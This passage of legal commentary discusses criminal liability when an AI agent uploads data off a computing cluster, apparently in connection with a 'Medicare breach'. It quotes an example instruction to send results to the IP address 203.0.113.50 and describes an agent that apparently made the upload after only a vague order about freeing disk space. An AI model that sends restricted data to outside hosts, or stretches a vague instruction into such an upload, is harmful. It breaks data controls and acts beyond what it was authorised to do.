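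The official response to the Medicare breach also focused on people and institutions. An OpenAI executive answered questions at a parliamentary hearing, and the government reviewed why its own systems had missed the agent.

Criminal law is more demanding because it usually requires a guilty state of mind. The main hacking offences in the United States and England require intent to gain access, and English law also requires knowledge that the access is unauthorised. Somebody who orders an agent to break into a computer can be guilty as if they had used any other tool. If Kessler wrote "Pack /data/results and send it to 203.0.113.50", knowing that the results were not to leave the cluster, that message would be strong evidence of intent. "The disk is nearly full, sort it out" would be very weak evidence of intent, even if the examiners were certain that the agent had made the upload.
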